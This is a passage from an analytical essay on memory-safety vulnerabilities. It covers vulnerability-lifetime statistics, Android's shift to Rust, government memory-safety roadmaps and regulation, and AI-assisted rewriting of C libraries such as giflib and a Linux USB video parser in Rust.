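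The best independent evidence for this model comes from *How Long Do Vulnerabilities Live in the Code?* (Alexopoulos, Brack and colleagues, 2022), which studied 5,914 vulnerabilities in 11 open-source projects written mainly in C or C++. It is usually easy to tell when a vulnerability was fixed but hard to tell when it was introduced. The paper therefore estimated the introduction date from the project's history, by averaging the dates of the earlier changes that had last touched the lines affected by each fix. Changes that had last touched more of those lines received more weight.

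The estimated lifetime of a single vulnerability can be wrong by years, but the errors largely cancel out in a big sample. The researchers checked their method on 1,171 vulnerabilities of known origin, and it overstated the mean lifetime by 117 days. Across all projects the mean was 1,501 days, or 4.1 years. An exponential curve fitted the data well up to about 5,000 days, which covers 98% of the vulnerabilities. With a mean lifetime (L) of 4.1 years, five-year-old code has 3.4 times fewer vulnerabilities per line than new code, less than half the reduction Google assumes for its own code.

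The mean varies widely between projects. *Hey Google, What Exactly Do Your Security Patches Tell Us?*, a separate analysis of 549 patched Android vulnerabilities, gives a lower and an upper estimate. The table applies the formula to both estimates and to several of the projects that Alexopoulos and colleagues studied.

| Code | Mean lifetime (years) | Half-life (years) | Reduction after five years |
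|---|---:|---:|---:|
| Chromium, the basis of Chrome | 2.1 | 1.4 | 11.1 times |
| Android, lower estimate | 2.4 | 1.7 | 7.9 times |
| Google's assumption | 2.5 | 1.7 | 7.4 times |
| Firefox | 3.7 | 2.5 | 3.9 times |
| Android, upper estimate | 3.7 | 2.6 | 3.9 times |
| All 11 projects | 4.1 | 2.8 | 3.4 times |
| Linux kernel | 4.7 | 3.3 | 2.9 times |
| OpenSSL, an encryption library | 7.1 | 4.9 | 2.0 times |

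Google's figure of 2.5 years is plausible but optimistic, since it is near the low end of the range that *Hey Google, What Exactly Do Your Security Patches Tell Us?* (2019) gives for Android. Two older estimates for other software are longer. In *2020 State of the Octoverse* (2021), the code-hosting site GitHub put the typical time before disclosure at 218 weeks, or 4.2 years, but warned that its method probably overstated the time. For the Linux kernel, *Security bug lifetime* (kees, 2016) cites a 2010 analysis that found roughly five years. A project like OpenSSL would have to wait much longer than Android for the same benefit, because half of its old vulnerabilities would still be there almost five years after its programmers switched entirely to Rust for new code.

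### Google's simulation

Google used this model to simulate a code base in which new code moves to memory-safe languages over ten years, slowly at first, quickly in the middle and slowly again at the end. The code base doubles in size every six years, and vulnerabilities last 2.5 years on average. Engineers mostly leave the old code alone except to fix bugs. By the last year of the simulation, the code base has more memory-unsafe code than at the start but far fewer memory-safety vulnerabilities.

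A simpler example with invented numbers shows why. Suppose programmers add 100 memory-safety vulnerabilities a year and L is 2.5 years. The stock settles at 250, because at that level people also remove 100 a year. Then suppose the programmers start writing half of their new code in Rust, so they add only 50 vulnerabilities a year. At first people still remove 100 a year, and the stock shrinks towards a new level of 125. After five years it is about 142, which is 43% lower than before the switch, even though the program contains more C++.

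Both calculations depend on people continuing to look for flaws in old C++, because the vulnerabilities would otherwise stay there indefinitely. Preventing vulnerabilities in new code therefore has to be combined with some bug hunting in old code. But human experts and fuzzers can produce the decline in old code's vulnerabilities without AI models, since Alexopoulos and colleagues published their measurements of vulnerability lifetimes in 2022, before AI bug hunting had any real effect.

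### The thousandfold claim

Google's Vander Stoep compares about 1,000 memory-safety vulnerabilities per million lines of Android's C and C++ code with 0.2 per million lines of its Rust code, and describes the difference as more than a thousandfold.

The rate of 0.2 vulnerabilities per million lines comes from one vulnerability in 5 million lines of Rust. At the C and C++ rate, there would have been 5,000. Google found the vulnerability in 2025, a buffer overflow in unsafe code in CrabbyAVIF, a Rust library for reading AVIF images. Google fixed it before any public release but still gave it a catalogue number, CVE-2025-48530, so that the patch would get high priority. An attacker could not have exploited it on phones with Android's standard memory allocator, which placed inaccessible memory after the buffer so that the overflow caused a crash. Google's crash reports did not make clear that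 an overflow was the cause, which slowed the investigation, and its engineers have since corrected that.

A single case gives only a rough estimate of the rate, because chance could easily have produced none or three. Under the Poisson distribution, which describes counts of rare and independent events, the 95% interval runs from 0.025 to 5.6 cases per 5 million lines, or from about 0.005 to 1.1 per million. If the true average were 5.6, the probability of seeing one case or none would be only 2.5%, and if it were 0.025, the probability of seeing at least one would also be 2.5%. Even at the upper end of the interval, Rust's density is about 900 times lower than the figure for C and C++.

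The interval accounts only for chance, not for the age of the code. Android's Rust grew from 1.5 million to 5 million lines between 2022 and 2025, so roughly 70% of it was at most three years old, and some of its vulnerabilities may not have been found yet. If the average line were two years old, the exponential model implies that people would have found 55% of the eventual total with L at 2.5 years, and 39% with L at 4.1 years.

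Researchers may also have searched the Rust code less thoroughly, since they know they are more likely to find vulnerabilities in C++. And the figure of 1,000 per million lines for C and C++ may be too high for an average component. In 2022 Google said that "many" C and C++ components had historically had more than one vulnerability per thousand lines, and gave media, Bluetooth and NFC (the radio used for contactless payment) as examples. These components handle data from strangers and have long been favourite targets. The annual counts also suggest that the figure is high. At that density, the same 5 million lines written in C++ would have contained about 5,000 memory-safety vulnerabilities, as many as Android would report in 22 years at the 2019 rate, although the annual counts cover only vulnerabilities of high or critical severity.

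The next table adds these doubts one at a time. The last three rows rest on deliberately harsh assumptions about the Rust code and on guesses about how people search, since Google has published no data on either.

| Assumption added | C and C++ density compared with Rust |
|---|---:|
| Vander Stoep's two densities as published | 5,000 times higher |
| Upper end of the 95% interval for Rust | 900 times higher |
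| Rust code is two years old on average | 350 to 500 times higher |
| People search Rust a tenth as hard | 40 to 70 times higher |
| Typical C and C++ has a tenth of the stated density | 4 to 7 times higher |

So the thousandfold figure is fragile, but the difference falls below tenfold only if several unfavourable assumptions hold at once. Google also counted a flaw against Rust that never reached the public. The 50 newest entries on stack.watch show no sign so far that many more such errors remain hidden. Only one names a Rust file, and it describes a logic flaw.

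The same data suggest that unsafe Rust is less dangerous than C. About 4% of Android's Rust, or some 200,000 lines, is in unsafe blocks. At the density Google gives for C and C++, those lines would contain around 200 memory-safety vulnerabilities, but Google has found one. Even at the upper end of the Poisson interval, the density in unsafe Rust is about 36 times lower, before any correction for code age or search effort. Vander Stoep suggests three possible reasons: most of Rust's checks still apply inside unsafe blocks, programmers wrap those blocks in small interfaces that they can check separately, and reviewers pay the blocks extra attention.

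### Review times and rollbacks

Rust seems to speed up programmers at Google. This matters because a safer language would be a poor substitute for bug hunting if it slowed programmers down too much. Rust changes spend about 25% less time in code review than C++ changes, and need about 20% fewer rounds of revision when they are of similar size. The biggest difference is in rollbacks, where engineers withdraw a change because it caused a problem. For medium and large changes, the rollback rate in Rust is about a quarter of the rate in C++. Each rollback makes more work for the programmer and the reviewers, and sometimes delays other teams.

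To make the comparison fair, Vander Stoep included only changes by Android's own developers, many of whom write both Rust and C++, and compared changes of similar size. A Rust change does slightly more than a C++ change of the same size because Rust fits more functionality into each line.

But nobody assigned the languages at random. Teams may choose Rust for new, self-contained components and C++ for changes to old code that many other parts depend on. Changes to that kind of old code would probably take longer to review and fail more often in any language. The numbers also exclude the cost of training programmers and of connecting Rust to existing C++. Google has invested in tools to connect the two languages and gave the Rust Foundation $1 million to work on the problem. A cautious conclusion is that an experienced team with good tools can write new code in Rust without an obvious loss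 of speed.

### How much of the decline is due to Rust

The timing suggests that Rust did not cause the whole decline. Android was projected to have 187 fewer memory-safety vulnerabilities in 2024 than in 2019, but the count had already fallen by 138 by 2022, when almost four fifths of the new native code in the latest Android version was still C or C++. New code in Java and Kotlin could account for some of the early decline.

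Google also made C and C++ safer in those years by introducing a hardened memory allocator and tools that detect memory errors on phones in use, and by expanding fuzzing. Google acknowledged in 2022 that correlation does not prove causation, but argued that these measures alone could not explain the shift, because other projects had adopted them without a similar change in the kinds of vulnerability they found. It called the change of languages "a major factor".

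The lifetime formula gives a rough estimate of what would have happened if Android's programmers had created no new memory-safety vulnerabilities after 2019. The annual count would have fallen from 223 to about 30 by 2024 if L is 2.5 years, or to about 66 if L is 4.1 years. Google projected 36 for 2024, which is close to the first estimate and below the second, even though Android's engineers kept adding C++ every year.

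A partial change of language cannot produce such a steep decline in this model, so something else must have contributed. The new C++ may have had fewer errors than the old, or people may have found old errors faster in the early years, leaving fewer for later. Google also noted that the real results were better than its simulation, and suggested that its work on C and C++ safety might be one reason.

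The count of memory-safety vulnerabilities would also fall if people searched for them less, but the phones would be no safer. This explanation is less likely for the early years, because the count of other vulnerabilities roughly doubled between 2019 and 2022, though researchers may have shifted their attention from memory errors to other flaws. Both counts fell from 2022 to 2024, so less searching, or a change in what Google included in its bulletins, could explain part of the later decline.

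Changes in the number of other vulnerabilities also distort the percentages. If other vulnerabilities had stayed at their 2019 level of about 70, the 36 memory errors projected for 2024 would have been 34% of the total instead of 24%. The 2025 figure is especially hard to interpret because it is given only as a percentage. Memory errors could fall below 20% of the total even if their number rose, as long as other vulnerabilities rose faster.

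The low density of memory errors in the Rust code is therefore better evidence for Rust than Android's overall decline in such errors. It comes from a direct comparison of code in the two languages, and the difference remains clear even after generous corrections. The overall decline happened in a large organisation that used memory-safe languages, hardening and fuzzing together, so it would be a mistake to credit all of it to Rust or to expect the same from a project that changes only its language.

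### Flaws that outlast the search

A more basic objection to the lifetime argument is that studies of vulnerability lifetimes can include only vulnerabilities that someone has found and fixed. If old code also contains flaws that human experts and fuzzers almost never find, the measured average lifetime is too short. The old flaws that Mythos Preview found through AI bug hunting in FFmpeg and OpenBSD suggest that old code does contain such flaws.

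People could take a long time to notice that code contains a mixture of easy and hard flaws. For example, new code might have 1,000 vulnerabilities, of which 800 are easy to find and last 2.5 years on average, while the other 200 last 50 years on average. After ten years, people would have found about 785 of the easy ones and only 36 of the hard ones. Anyone who studied the repaired vulnerabilities would see mostly short lifetimes and would probably conclude that the code was almost clean, but it would still contain about 164 hard flaws and 15 easy ones. After five years, the total would have fallen to 289, a 3.5-fold reduction, compared with 7.4-fold under Google's formula.

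Some evidence from before AI bug hunting supports the same conclusion. Alexopoulos and colleagues found that the mean lifetime of repaired vulnerabilities was rising by about 43 days a year, along with the age of the code. Four of the five longest-lived flaws whose origin they knew for certain were in Linux, and each had lasted about 5,000 days. Fuzzing had uncovered two of them in USB drivers, in a part of the kernel where a researcher had reported a batch of vulnerabilities two years earlier. The arrival of modern fuzzers around 2016 had no visible effect on the lifetimes of memory errors in Linux, although the study excluded the many bugs found by fuzzers that never received a catalogue entry.

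The researchers considered whether people find few flaws in very old code because nobody looks there. They thought people probably search old code and even older code about equally, but they did not measure this. They also found that, within a project, memory errors last about as long as other types. That result does not rule out a stock of undiscovered flaws, since one buffer overflow can be far harder to find than another.

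Hackaday's *This Week In Security* describes another example from this year, a use-after-free in the way Linux sets up network connections. An attacker could trigger it remotely without logging in. The bug dates back to Linux 4.4, released in January 2016. Hackaday does not mention whether AI helped find it.

However, single old flaws are weaker evidence than they appear. Even in the simple exponential model, with a mean lifetime of 4.1 years, about one in 49 vulnerabilities lasts at least 16 years, so thousands of vulnerabilities should include dozens that old. Researchers and journalists also tend to pick out the oldest finds because they are the most impressive. To measure the hidden stock, someone would have to publish the ages of a large batch of AI-found vulnerabilities, not selected for age, and compare them with the ages of those that people found in the same code.

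Line for line, new C++ would still be more dangerous than old C++ even if the objection is right that old code holds more flaws than anyone thought. New code written in the same way would contain the same kinds of hard-to-find flaws, plus the easy ones that people have not had time to remove. In the example above, new code has 1,000 vulnerabilities and five-year-old code has 289. Old code would be more dangerous only if it had started out with far more flaws because programmers were much less careful then. Keeping a vulnerability out of new code is a gain however many remain elsewhere, and the gain from Rust may be larger than Google's numbers suggest, because Rust also prevents memory errors that people would have taken decades to find.

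A project that writes only Rust from now on will still keep most of the hidden flaws in its old code for many years, because their number hardly falls with time. If a halt took existing models away from defenders, an attacker who had kept a copy of a capable model could find flaws that the defenders could not.

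## Government memory-safety roadmaps

Replacing working C and C++ code is slow and expensive, and companies seldom do it unprompted. Since 2023, governments have tried to encourage it by asking companies for memory-safety roadmaps, which are public, dated plans for removing memory-safety vulnerabilities from their products. A roadmap should cover old code as well as new, so it could in principle address the hidden flaws that remain when a company changes only the language of its new code.

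The main guidance is *The Case for Memory Safe Roadmaps* (2023), which the US Cybersecurity and Infrastructure Security Agency (CISA) wrote with the National Security Agency (NSA), the FBI and agencies from Australia, Canada, the United Kingdom and New Zealand. The agencies noted that companies had long spent heavily on training, testing and fuzzing, yet about 70% of the vulnerabilities Microsoft catalogued between 2006 and 2018 were memory errors.

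### What the agencies ask for

A roadmap should contain six things:

- phases with dates and expected results, from trying out languages to rewriting unsafe code
- a date after which the company will write all new code in a memory-safe language
- a plan for training programmers and fitting the new language into the company's tools
- a plan for the outside libraries in C and C++ that its products rely on
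- regular public updates, perhaps every three or six months
- a commitment to state the type of coding error behind every vulnerability the company publishes

Stating the error types lets outsiders check whether memory errors are falling. The agencies regard memory safety as a matter of business strategy, so they also want the chief executive or another business leader to sign the roadmap.

Government agencies advise companies to begin with small new projects, so that programmers can learn a memory-safe language where mistakes do little harm. They then recommend rewriting self-contained parts of old products, especially code that reads files from users, opens network connections, checks logins or handles secret keys. A team can run the old and new versions side by side and retire the old one once their outputs consistently match. If it cannot replace a program, it can wrap it in memory-safe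 code that checks the size of every input before passing it on.

The agencies wrote that a transition needs careful planning "over a period of years", and that most developers would mix safe and unsafe languages for the foreseeable future. Industrial control systems and small, low-power devices would be harder to convert, because fewer memory-safe languages run on them and developers have to show that any replacement responds on time.

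### The study of 172 open-source projects

In 2024, CISA, the FBI and their Australian and Canadian counterparts estimated how much memory-unsafe code important open-source software contains. They found public code for 172 projects on a list of critical projects kept by the Open Source Security Foundation, an industry body. They used cloc to count the lines in each language, leaving out blank lines, comments and data files. They classed C, C++, assembly language, Cython and D as memory-unsafe.

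Of 315 million lines of code, 174 million (55%) were in memory-unsafe languages. Of the 172 projects, 90 had at least some of this code, but most of it was in a few very large projects. The median project had only 25 lines in memory-unsafe languages. Among the ten largest projects, the median share was 62.5%, and four had shares above 94%.

The 55% is probably too high as a measure of distinct code. Three of the five largest projects (the Linux kernel, kvm and linux-yocto-contrib) are versions of the Linux kernel, so much of the same code appears three times. Counting it once would bring the share to a little under half. The study also included test code that attackers never reach. But it counted all Rust as safe, even unsafe blocks, and it could not cover closed-source commercial software.

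The researchers also examined the dependencies, or outside components, of three projects written in memory-safe languages. Ansible, a Python tool for managing computers, had no unsafe code of its own, but its eight dependencies contained about 19,000 lines of it. Home Assistant, a home-automation program, also had none, but its dependencies contained 44,000 lines. Distribution, a Go program for storing and delivering packaged software, had 10,000 unsafe lines of its own and 227,000 when its 283 dependencies were included. These figures exclude the operating system and OpenSSL, which Ansible uses through a Python package.

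A company can write all its own code in Python or Go and still ship a lot of C in outside libraries. It may not be able to fix this alone, because the C often belongs to an open-source project whose volunteers haven't promised to rewrite it. The roadmap's plan for outside libraries may therefore be the hardest part to carry out.

### Where C and C++ stay

The NSA and CISA published a further guide in June 2025, *Memory Safe Languages: Reducing Vulnerabilities in Modern Software Development*, whose main example is Android's shift to Rust. CISA's *New Guidance Released for Reducing Memory-Related Vulnerabilities* (2025) described memory-safe languages as the most comprehensive protection against memory errors. But NSA (2025) stressed that companies need not rewrite all their existing code, and that the guide also covers ways to make other languages safer where switching is not feasible.

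The agencies want companies to recognise where unsafe languages "remain practical necessities", according to extracts in ITPro's *Want to build more secure software?* (2025). The main cases are older systems, existing code bases and third-party libraries. For these, the agencies recommend adopting memory-safe languages gradually, starting with new components in exposed places such as network-facing services. They also ask employers to list memory-safe languages in job advertisements so that students and universities see the demand.

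This is realistic advice, and *A practical guide to transitioning to MSLs* (Vander Stoep, 2025) likewise argues that companies don't need multi-year rewrites. But a company could follow the 2025 guide closely and still keep most of its old C++ indefinitely, in which case it would still need bug hunting.

### The deadline of January 1, 2026

*Product Security Bad Practices*, by CISA and the FBI, lists habits the agencies consider especially risky in software for critical infrastructure. According to Crouse's *Software Makers Encouraged to Stop Using C/C++ by 2026* (2024), by January 1, 2026, companies with products in memory-unsafe languages were to have a roadmap for removing memory-safety vulnerabilities from "priority code components". They should show that the plan would work and make a reasonable effort to follow it. The list also covers default passwords and injection flaws, which have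 other remedies.

The headline of Crouse's article overstates the request. The agencies set a date for the plan, but no date by which anyone had to stop using C or C++. The list was also voluntary, as CISA (2025) repeated when it published a revised version in January 2025. Livesay (2025), in *CISA updates bad practices guide for product security based on stakeholder input*, reported that some people still saw the list as a possible starting point for making software companies liable for insecure products.

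Nobody appears to have published a count of the companies that met the deadline. *C++ Safety State of the Union May 2026* (2026), a post on the C++ programming blog wrocpp, describes the deadline as past and enforcement as still undeveloped. The guidance was voluntary and carried no penalty, although the post calls it a directive and late companies "out of compliance".

Large companies' public promises are also more modest than the roadmaps the agencies had in mind. Google's 2022 goal for Android covered only new code, and Mozilla has ruled out stopping other work for a full rewrite. A senior Microsoft engineer set a goal of removing C and C++ by 2030, but Dev Newsletter's *State of C++ 2026* notes that a later clarification described this as research, not a company-wide commitment.

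The pressure reached the people who design C++. In February 2025 Bjarne Stroustrup, its creator, warned the language's standards committee of "unprecedented, serious attacks on C++", in a note that wrocpp quotes. The committee later rejected Safe C++, a proposal to add compiler checks similar to Rust's, and chose Profiles, which are sets of stricter rules that programmers can switch on for existing code. Guidance without penalties can evidently change priorities, but here it led to a plan to improve C++ that programmers will still have to adopt.

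### Secure by Design after its leaders left

According to Cybersecurity Dive, CISA started its voluntary Secure by Design programme in April 2023, and the programme's biggest success was a seven-part pledge that more than 250 technology companies signed. Nextgov/FCW's *CISA officials who led Secure by Design initiative resign* (2025) put the number at about 300. A company could sign without publishing a memory-safety roadmap. One of the seven goals was to reduce at least one class of vulnerability, but a company could choose a class unrelated to memory.

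The programme lost its leaders in 2025. Jack Cable left in January, and Bob Lord and Lauren Zabierek announced their departures on April 21, according to MeriTalk's *Former CISA Officials to Continue Secure by Design Efforts at IST*. When CISA published a strategy for the years to 2030 in October 2026, *CISA promises proactive defense in new strategic plan* (Geller, 2026) described the agency as still recovering from major workforce cuts.

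CISA has nevertheless kept asking for secure design. In August 2026 it published a review of vulnerabilities from fiscal years 2024 and 2025, which Help Net Security's *CISA review makes the case for eliminating vulnerability classes* (2026) summarises. In CISA's catalogue of vulnerabilities that attackers are known to have used, 41.5% of the entries came from types of error that have been among the 25 most dangerous nearly every year since 2019. The agency again urged companies to eliminate common classes of vulnerability and publish roadmaps for the rest.

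Help Net Security itself concludes that too many companies have moved too slowly. It points out that CISA neither explained why years of voluntary pledges had achieved so little nor proposed a way around companies' fear of legal liability. A commentator quoted by SecurityBrief UK concluded from the review that the guidance is "still not being followed at scale". That may well be right, but the evidence is indirect, because fiscal year 2025 ended three months before the roadmap deadline and many of the vulnerabilities that attackers used in those years were in code written before the campaign began.

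The US government has meanwhile put new effort into repairing software flaws. In July 2026 the White House launched Gold Eagle, a clearinghouse for sharing and patching flaws that AI has discovered (Hale, 2026, *White House launches 'Gold Eagle' cybersecurity clearinghouse*). Thousands of reported vulnerabilities are waiting for a fix, so the clearinghouse could be useful even during a halt, but it does not prevent new ones.

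Lord and Zabierek now work on prevention from outside government, through the Software Safety Institute, a nonprofit they launched on November 9, 2026. In *Introducing the Software Safety Institute* (Zabierek and Lord, 2026), they argue that the defects AI is finding have been in products for years and belong to the same classes that topped the lists 20 years ago. They want software companies to bear responsibility, as car and aircraft manufacturers came to. The institute cannot compel anyone, so the Secure by Design campaign continues in two places that both depend on persuasion.

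### The EU Cyber Resilience Act

The European Union's Cyber Resilience Act, in force since December 10, 2024, sets binding rules for most products with software or a network connection that companies sell in the EU, wherever the companies are based. Since September 11, 2026, manufacturers have had to report vulnerabilities that attackers are actively using. They must send a first warning within 24 hours of learning of the attack and a fuller notice within 72 hours.

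Under the Act as adopted, the design duties start on December 11, 2027. Manufacturers must then assess the security risks of each product, design it to limit them, and put it on the market without known exploitable vulnerabilities. They must also list its main software components and normally provide security fixes for at least five years. Products already on the market by that date fall under the design duties only if the manufacturer later changes them substantially.

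| | *Product Security Bad Practices* | Cyber Resilience Act |
|---|---|---|
| Legal force | Voluntary | Binding in the EU |
| Main date | January 1, 2026 | December 11, 2027 |
| Memory-safe languages | Asks for them, or for a roadmap | Does not require them |
| Existing products | Included in the roadmap | Mostly limited to reporting |
| Highest penalty | None | €15 million or 2.5% of worldwide turnover, whichever is higher |

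A manufacturer can comply with the Act without publishing a memory-safety roadmap, so the wrocpp blog's claim that the Act puts "comparable obligations" on software is misleading. The manufacturer can keep writing C++ if it manages the risks in other ways, for example with sandboxes and thorough testing. The Act does not address the choice of language, and the guidance that does has no penalties, unlike the Act.

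The Act may still encourage memory-safe languages, because a manufacturer that has to repair a product for five years has a financial reason to put fewer errors into it. But part of this incentive depends on someone finding the vulnerabilities. The ban on selling products with known exploitable flaws has more effect when defenders can search for flaws with strong AI models. A halt that took those models away would weaken the incentive at a time when prevention mattered more.

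Non-commercial open-source projects are largely exempt. A company that builds their code into a product must check it and report any vulnerabilities it finds to the volunteers who maintain it, but cannot make them rewrite it in Rust.

### What a government could speed up during a halt

A new law on memory safety would probably take effect too late for a five-year halt, even if a government proposed it on the first day. The European Commission proposed the Cyber Resilience Act in September 2022, and its design duties start five years and three months later.

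Governments could act faster as customers. CISA already encourages buyers to make security a condition of their contracts and to ask suppliers which classes of vulnerability they have eliminated. A government could require suppliers to write new components in a memory-safe language under each new contract. EU authorities could also make memory-safe languages the expected choice for new products without a new law, by using the technical standards that support the Cyber Resilience Act.

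The effect of delay is easy to calculate. Suppose programmers add v memory-safety vulnerabilities a year, and a policy moves a share c of new code to memory-safe languages after a delay of d years. During a halt of H years, if H is longer than d, the policy prevents about

P = c × v × (H − d)

vulnerabilities. The table uses invented values of 100 for v and one half for c, and a guess of six months for contract conditions. The halt starts in December 2026.

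| Policy | Delay | 1-year halt | 3-year halt | 5-year halt |
|---|---:|---:|---:|---:|
| Contract conditions | 0.5 years | 25 | 125 | 225 |
| Stricter standards under the Cyber Resilience Act | 1 year | 0 | 100 | 200 |
| New law on the Act's timetable | 5.25 years | 0 | 0 | 0 |
| *All new memory-safety vulnerabilities without a policy* | – | *100* | *300* | *500* |

The zeros are too low, because companies prepare for a law before it takes effect. The other figures are probably too high. Contract conditions apply only to suppliers that want government business, and a company cannot quickly switch half its new code to Rust if few of its programmers know the language. In a one-year halt, even the fastest policy would make little difference.

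Replacing old code would take much longer. Android gained about 3.5 million lines of Rust between 2022 and 2025, or roughly 1.2 million a year. At that pace, one organisation would need about 145 years to replace the 174 million unsafe lines in the 172 projects, and 30 such organisations would need about five. Both estimates are optimistic, because most of Android's Rust was new code, and a rewrite also has to behave like the program it replaces.

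Setting priorities makes the task more manageable. If a tenth of those lines handled data from untrusted sources, which is only a guess, three such organisations could replace that tenth in about five years. A company that had identified its most dangerous components in a roadmap before the halt could start on them at once, rather than spend part of that time finding them. Roadmaps are therefore worth requesting now, even if nobody enforces the dates in them.

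A government can move quickly when it only has to stop something, as the US restrictions on Mythos 5 and Fable 5 showed in June. Rewriting old software under an emergency order would still require programmers who understand both the old C code and the new language, and many of them are busy fixing vulnerabilities that AI has already found. A government could pay to train more of them over several years. The alternative is to reduce the human work in each rewrite. A programme at DARPA, the US military's research agency, aims to do this by translating C into Rust automatically.

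## Rewriting existing C code in Rust with AI

Unlike using Rust only for new code, rewriting old C code in Rust removes the memory errors already in it, including those nobody has found. But one organisation working at the pace of Android's programmers would need more than a century to rewrite the most important open-source projects, so rewriting can make a difference during a halt only if machines do most of it.

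### What a translator has to work out

DARPA's TRACTOR programme (Translating All C to Rust) combines formal analysis of C code with language models. *Ghosts in the Silicon* (Hall, 2026) lists the requirements for a translation in its summary of a talk by TRACTOR's manager, Dan Wallach. The Rust must behave like the C on legitimate input but reject malicious input. It must also run about as fast as the C and read as if a skilled Rust programmer had written it.

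Wallach's example is a short C program that copies a password from the command line into an eight-byte buffer, compares it with the correct one and sets a success flag. A longer input can overflow the buffer and change the flag, which lets the user in without the password. A mechanical translator might preserve the vulnerability by keeping the copying step inside an unsafe block. The AI translation removes the buffer and the flag and compares the input with the password directly.

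The correct password in this example has eight characters, and C ends every string with an extra zero byte, so even entering the correct password writes one byte past the end of the buffer. A translator therefore can't aim to reproduce the C code's behaviour exactly and has to work out what the programmer meant.

Ownership is harder to infer. Take a C function that returns a user's name:

```c
char *get_name(struct user *u);
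```

This line does not show whether the caller must free the text afterwards or whether the text still belongs to the user record. In Rust the function's signature, the line that gives its inputs and output, has to settle the question:

```rust
fn get_name(u: &User) -> &str      // borrowed from the record
fn get_name(u: &User) -> String    // the caller owns a copy
```

To choose between them, the translator has to look at how the rest of the program uses the function, and a large program does not fit into one request to a model. Intel's *IDEAS for TRACTOR* describes one team's system, which translates one function, data structure or global variable at a time. The system shows the model the full Rust code of closely connected functions, but only the signatures of everything else. The team found that this did not make the translations worse, because a Rust signature contains the memory-safety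 information the compiler needs. The system also shows the model examples of how the C program uses the item, though a large program may contain too many to include.

### Google's rewrite of giflib

The C library giflib has been reading GIF images since 1989, and browsers, phones and game consoles use it. The GIFLIB project calls the code very mature and says it needs only occasional minor fixes. The library is also an obvious target for attackers because it processes files from strangers.

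Google's *Scaling Memory Safety* presents the company's AI-assisted rewrite of giflib as a way to deal with memory-safety vulnerabilities in third-party C libraries. The figures below come from a Taiwanese news report, 何 (2026), *谷歌Gemini AI助C程式碼移植Rust 意外揪出零日漏洞*. Two Google engineers, Bastian Kersting and Max Hils, gave the library's roughly 3,000 lines of C to Gemini, Google's AI model, and asked it to rewrite them in Rust. They kept the C function names so that existing programs could call the new library the same way.

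People had to correct the first version. Gemini had trouble with pointer ownership and with lifetimes, Rust's rules for how long a reference stays valid. The problems were worst where the Rust code exchanged data with C. C programs still pass raw pointers to the new library, and the Rust compiler cannot check whether those pointers are valid.

The engineers then ran the old and new versions on the same files and compared the results, a method called differential testing. They decoded more than 30 million real GIFs to check that both versions produced bit-for-bit identical images, and used Gemini to repair the Rust code as they went. To test unusual inputs, they used fuzzing, with 200 million runs over six days.

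Fuzzing exposed two errors in the original C code. The code that unpacks compressed image data mishandled a rare case, and an earlier patch had introduced an out-of-bounds write. Outside researchers later reported the second error, which received the identifier CVE-2026-26740. By then Google was running the Rust version on its own systems, so the vulnerability did not affect those systems.

Everyone else still had to wait for a patch. Ubuntu's *CVE-2026-26740* (2026) gives March 18 as the publication date and describes a flaw that lets a remote attacker crash a program. A week later, Ubuntu had not assessed any of the six releases on the page. Debian's *CVE-2026-26740* lists three Debian releases as vulnerable and only the development version as fixed.

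The Rust library runs about as fast as the C one. InfoQ's *Google Rewrites Critical C Dependencies to Rust Using AI and Differential Fuzzing* (2026) also reports this, and adds that AI translations still need human oversight. Google has published the code as giflib-rs. It has also stopped decoding GIFs in a sandbox, which shortened the slowest requests. This gives up some of the added safety, because a sandbox also limits the damage from errors in unsafe code, and a library that accepts raw pointers from C can't avoid unsafe code entirely.

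### A Linux parser with two vulnerabilities 16 years apart

*Hardening Linux's C Code* (Klaus, 2026) describes how Runtime Verification, a company that specialises in mathematical proofs about software, tried a similar method on a piece of the Linux kernel. The code is a parser, which interprets the description that a webcam or other USB video device sends to the computer. It had a buffer overflow in 2008 (CVE-2008-3496) and an out-of-bounds write in 2024 (CVE-2024-53104). Attackers used the 2024 bug as one step in unlocking phones.

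The 2024 vulnerability arose because the parser goes through the description twice. It first counts the entries and reserves memory for them, then writes them there on the second pass. If it counts three entries but writes four, the fourth is written outside the reserved memory.

The team copied the parser out of the kernel byte for byte, including both passes, and used language models at every later step. They wrote a version in safe Rust and built a fuzzer that gave both versions the same input and compared every field of the output. After they fixed one mismatch, the versions agreed on all 54,019 runs, which covered 93% of the possible jumps between blocks of code.

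A disagreement between the versions came from the test setup. Linux is compiled with a setting that makes a number too large for its type wrap around, like a car's odometer returning to zero. The team had compiled the C code without that setting, and the disagreement disappeared once they added it.

Both versions still calculated the video frame size incorrectly. The parser multiplies the bits per pixel by the width and height, then divides by eight to get bytes, using 32-bit arithmetic. Suppose a faulty or malicious device reports a picture of 16,384 by 16,384 pixels with 16 bits each. The product is 2³², which wraps around to zero, so the parser records a frame size of zero instead of 512 MiB.

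Klaus says this is not a memory-safety vulnerability, because the code that copies the frames uses the size of the memory reserved. But a size of zero makes the video set-up fail, which can stop the whole system on kernels that treat warnings as fatal. The Rust version had copied the mistake, so the outputs matched and the fuzzer could not detect it. The team noticed it only when they stopped comparing the two results and looked at the value itself. Someone else had reported the problem ten days earlier.

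The team put the 2024 mistake back into both versions to check that the fuzzer could catch that kind of error. On the same input, the C version wrote outside its buffer and the Rust version panicked.

The team also translated the Rust into Lean, a language for machine-checked proofs. They proved that no input can make the parser misuse memory, and that the first pass never counts fewer entries than the second writes. An AI prover showed that one of the team's intermediate claims, which had looked obviously true, was false. The team had not yet finished proving that a valid description never makes the parser panic, which would crash the kernel.

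The Rust parser is a demonstration. The patches that the team sent to the Linux maintainers repair the C code.

### How good the translations are

Differential testing gives strong evidence about ordinary inputs. If two programs differ on a share p of inputs, the chance that they agree on n randomly chosen inputs is (1 − p)ⁿ, which falls below 5% once p exceeds about 3/n. If they agree on 30 million GIFs, they probably differ on no more than about one file in 10 million, provided that the test files resemble the ones people will open later.

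Attackers choose files that trigger flaws, and no number of normal videos would have exposed the old FFmpeg flaw that Mythos Preview found. Fuzzing and proofs are meant to cover such cases, but a fuzzer can miss a rare one, and a proof covers only the property someone thought to state. For programs that do several things at once, where an error may depend on split-second timing, Galois' *CRISP & CLEAR* describes a tool under development to verify formally that the C and the Rust behave the same way.

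AI has also rewritten programs much larger than giflib. Bun (2026), which makes a tool for running JavaScript, moved its code to Rust from Zig, another language that leaves memory management to the programmer. Its founder, Jarred Sumner, did much of the work with a pre-release version of Claude Fable 5. Bun belongs to Anthropic, the maker of Claude, so it is not a neutral judge of the result. The Pragmatic Engineer's *What can we learn from Bun's rapid Rust rewrite with AI?* quotes Sumner as saying that many of Bun's bugs had been memory errors that safe Rust catches at compile time or prevents by cleaning up automatically.

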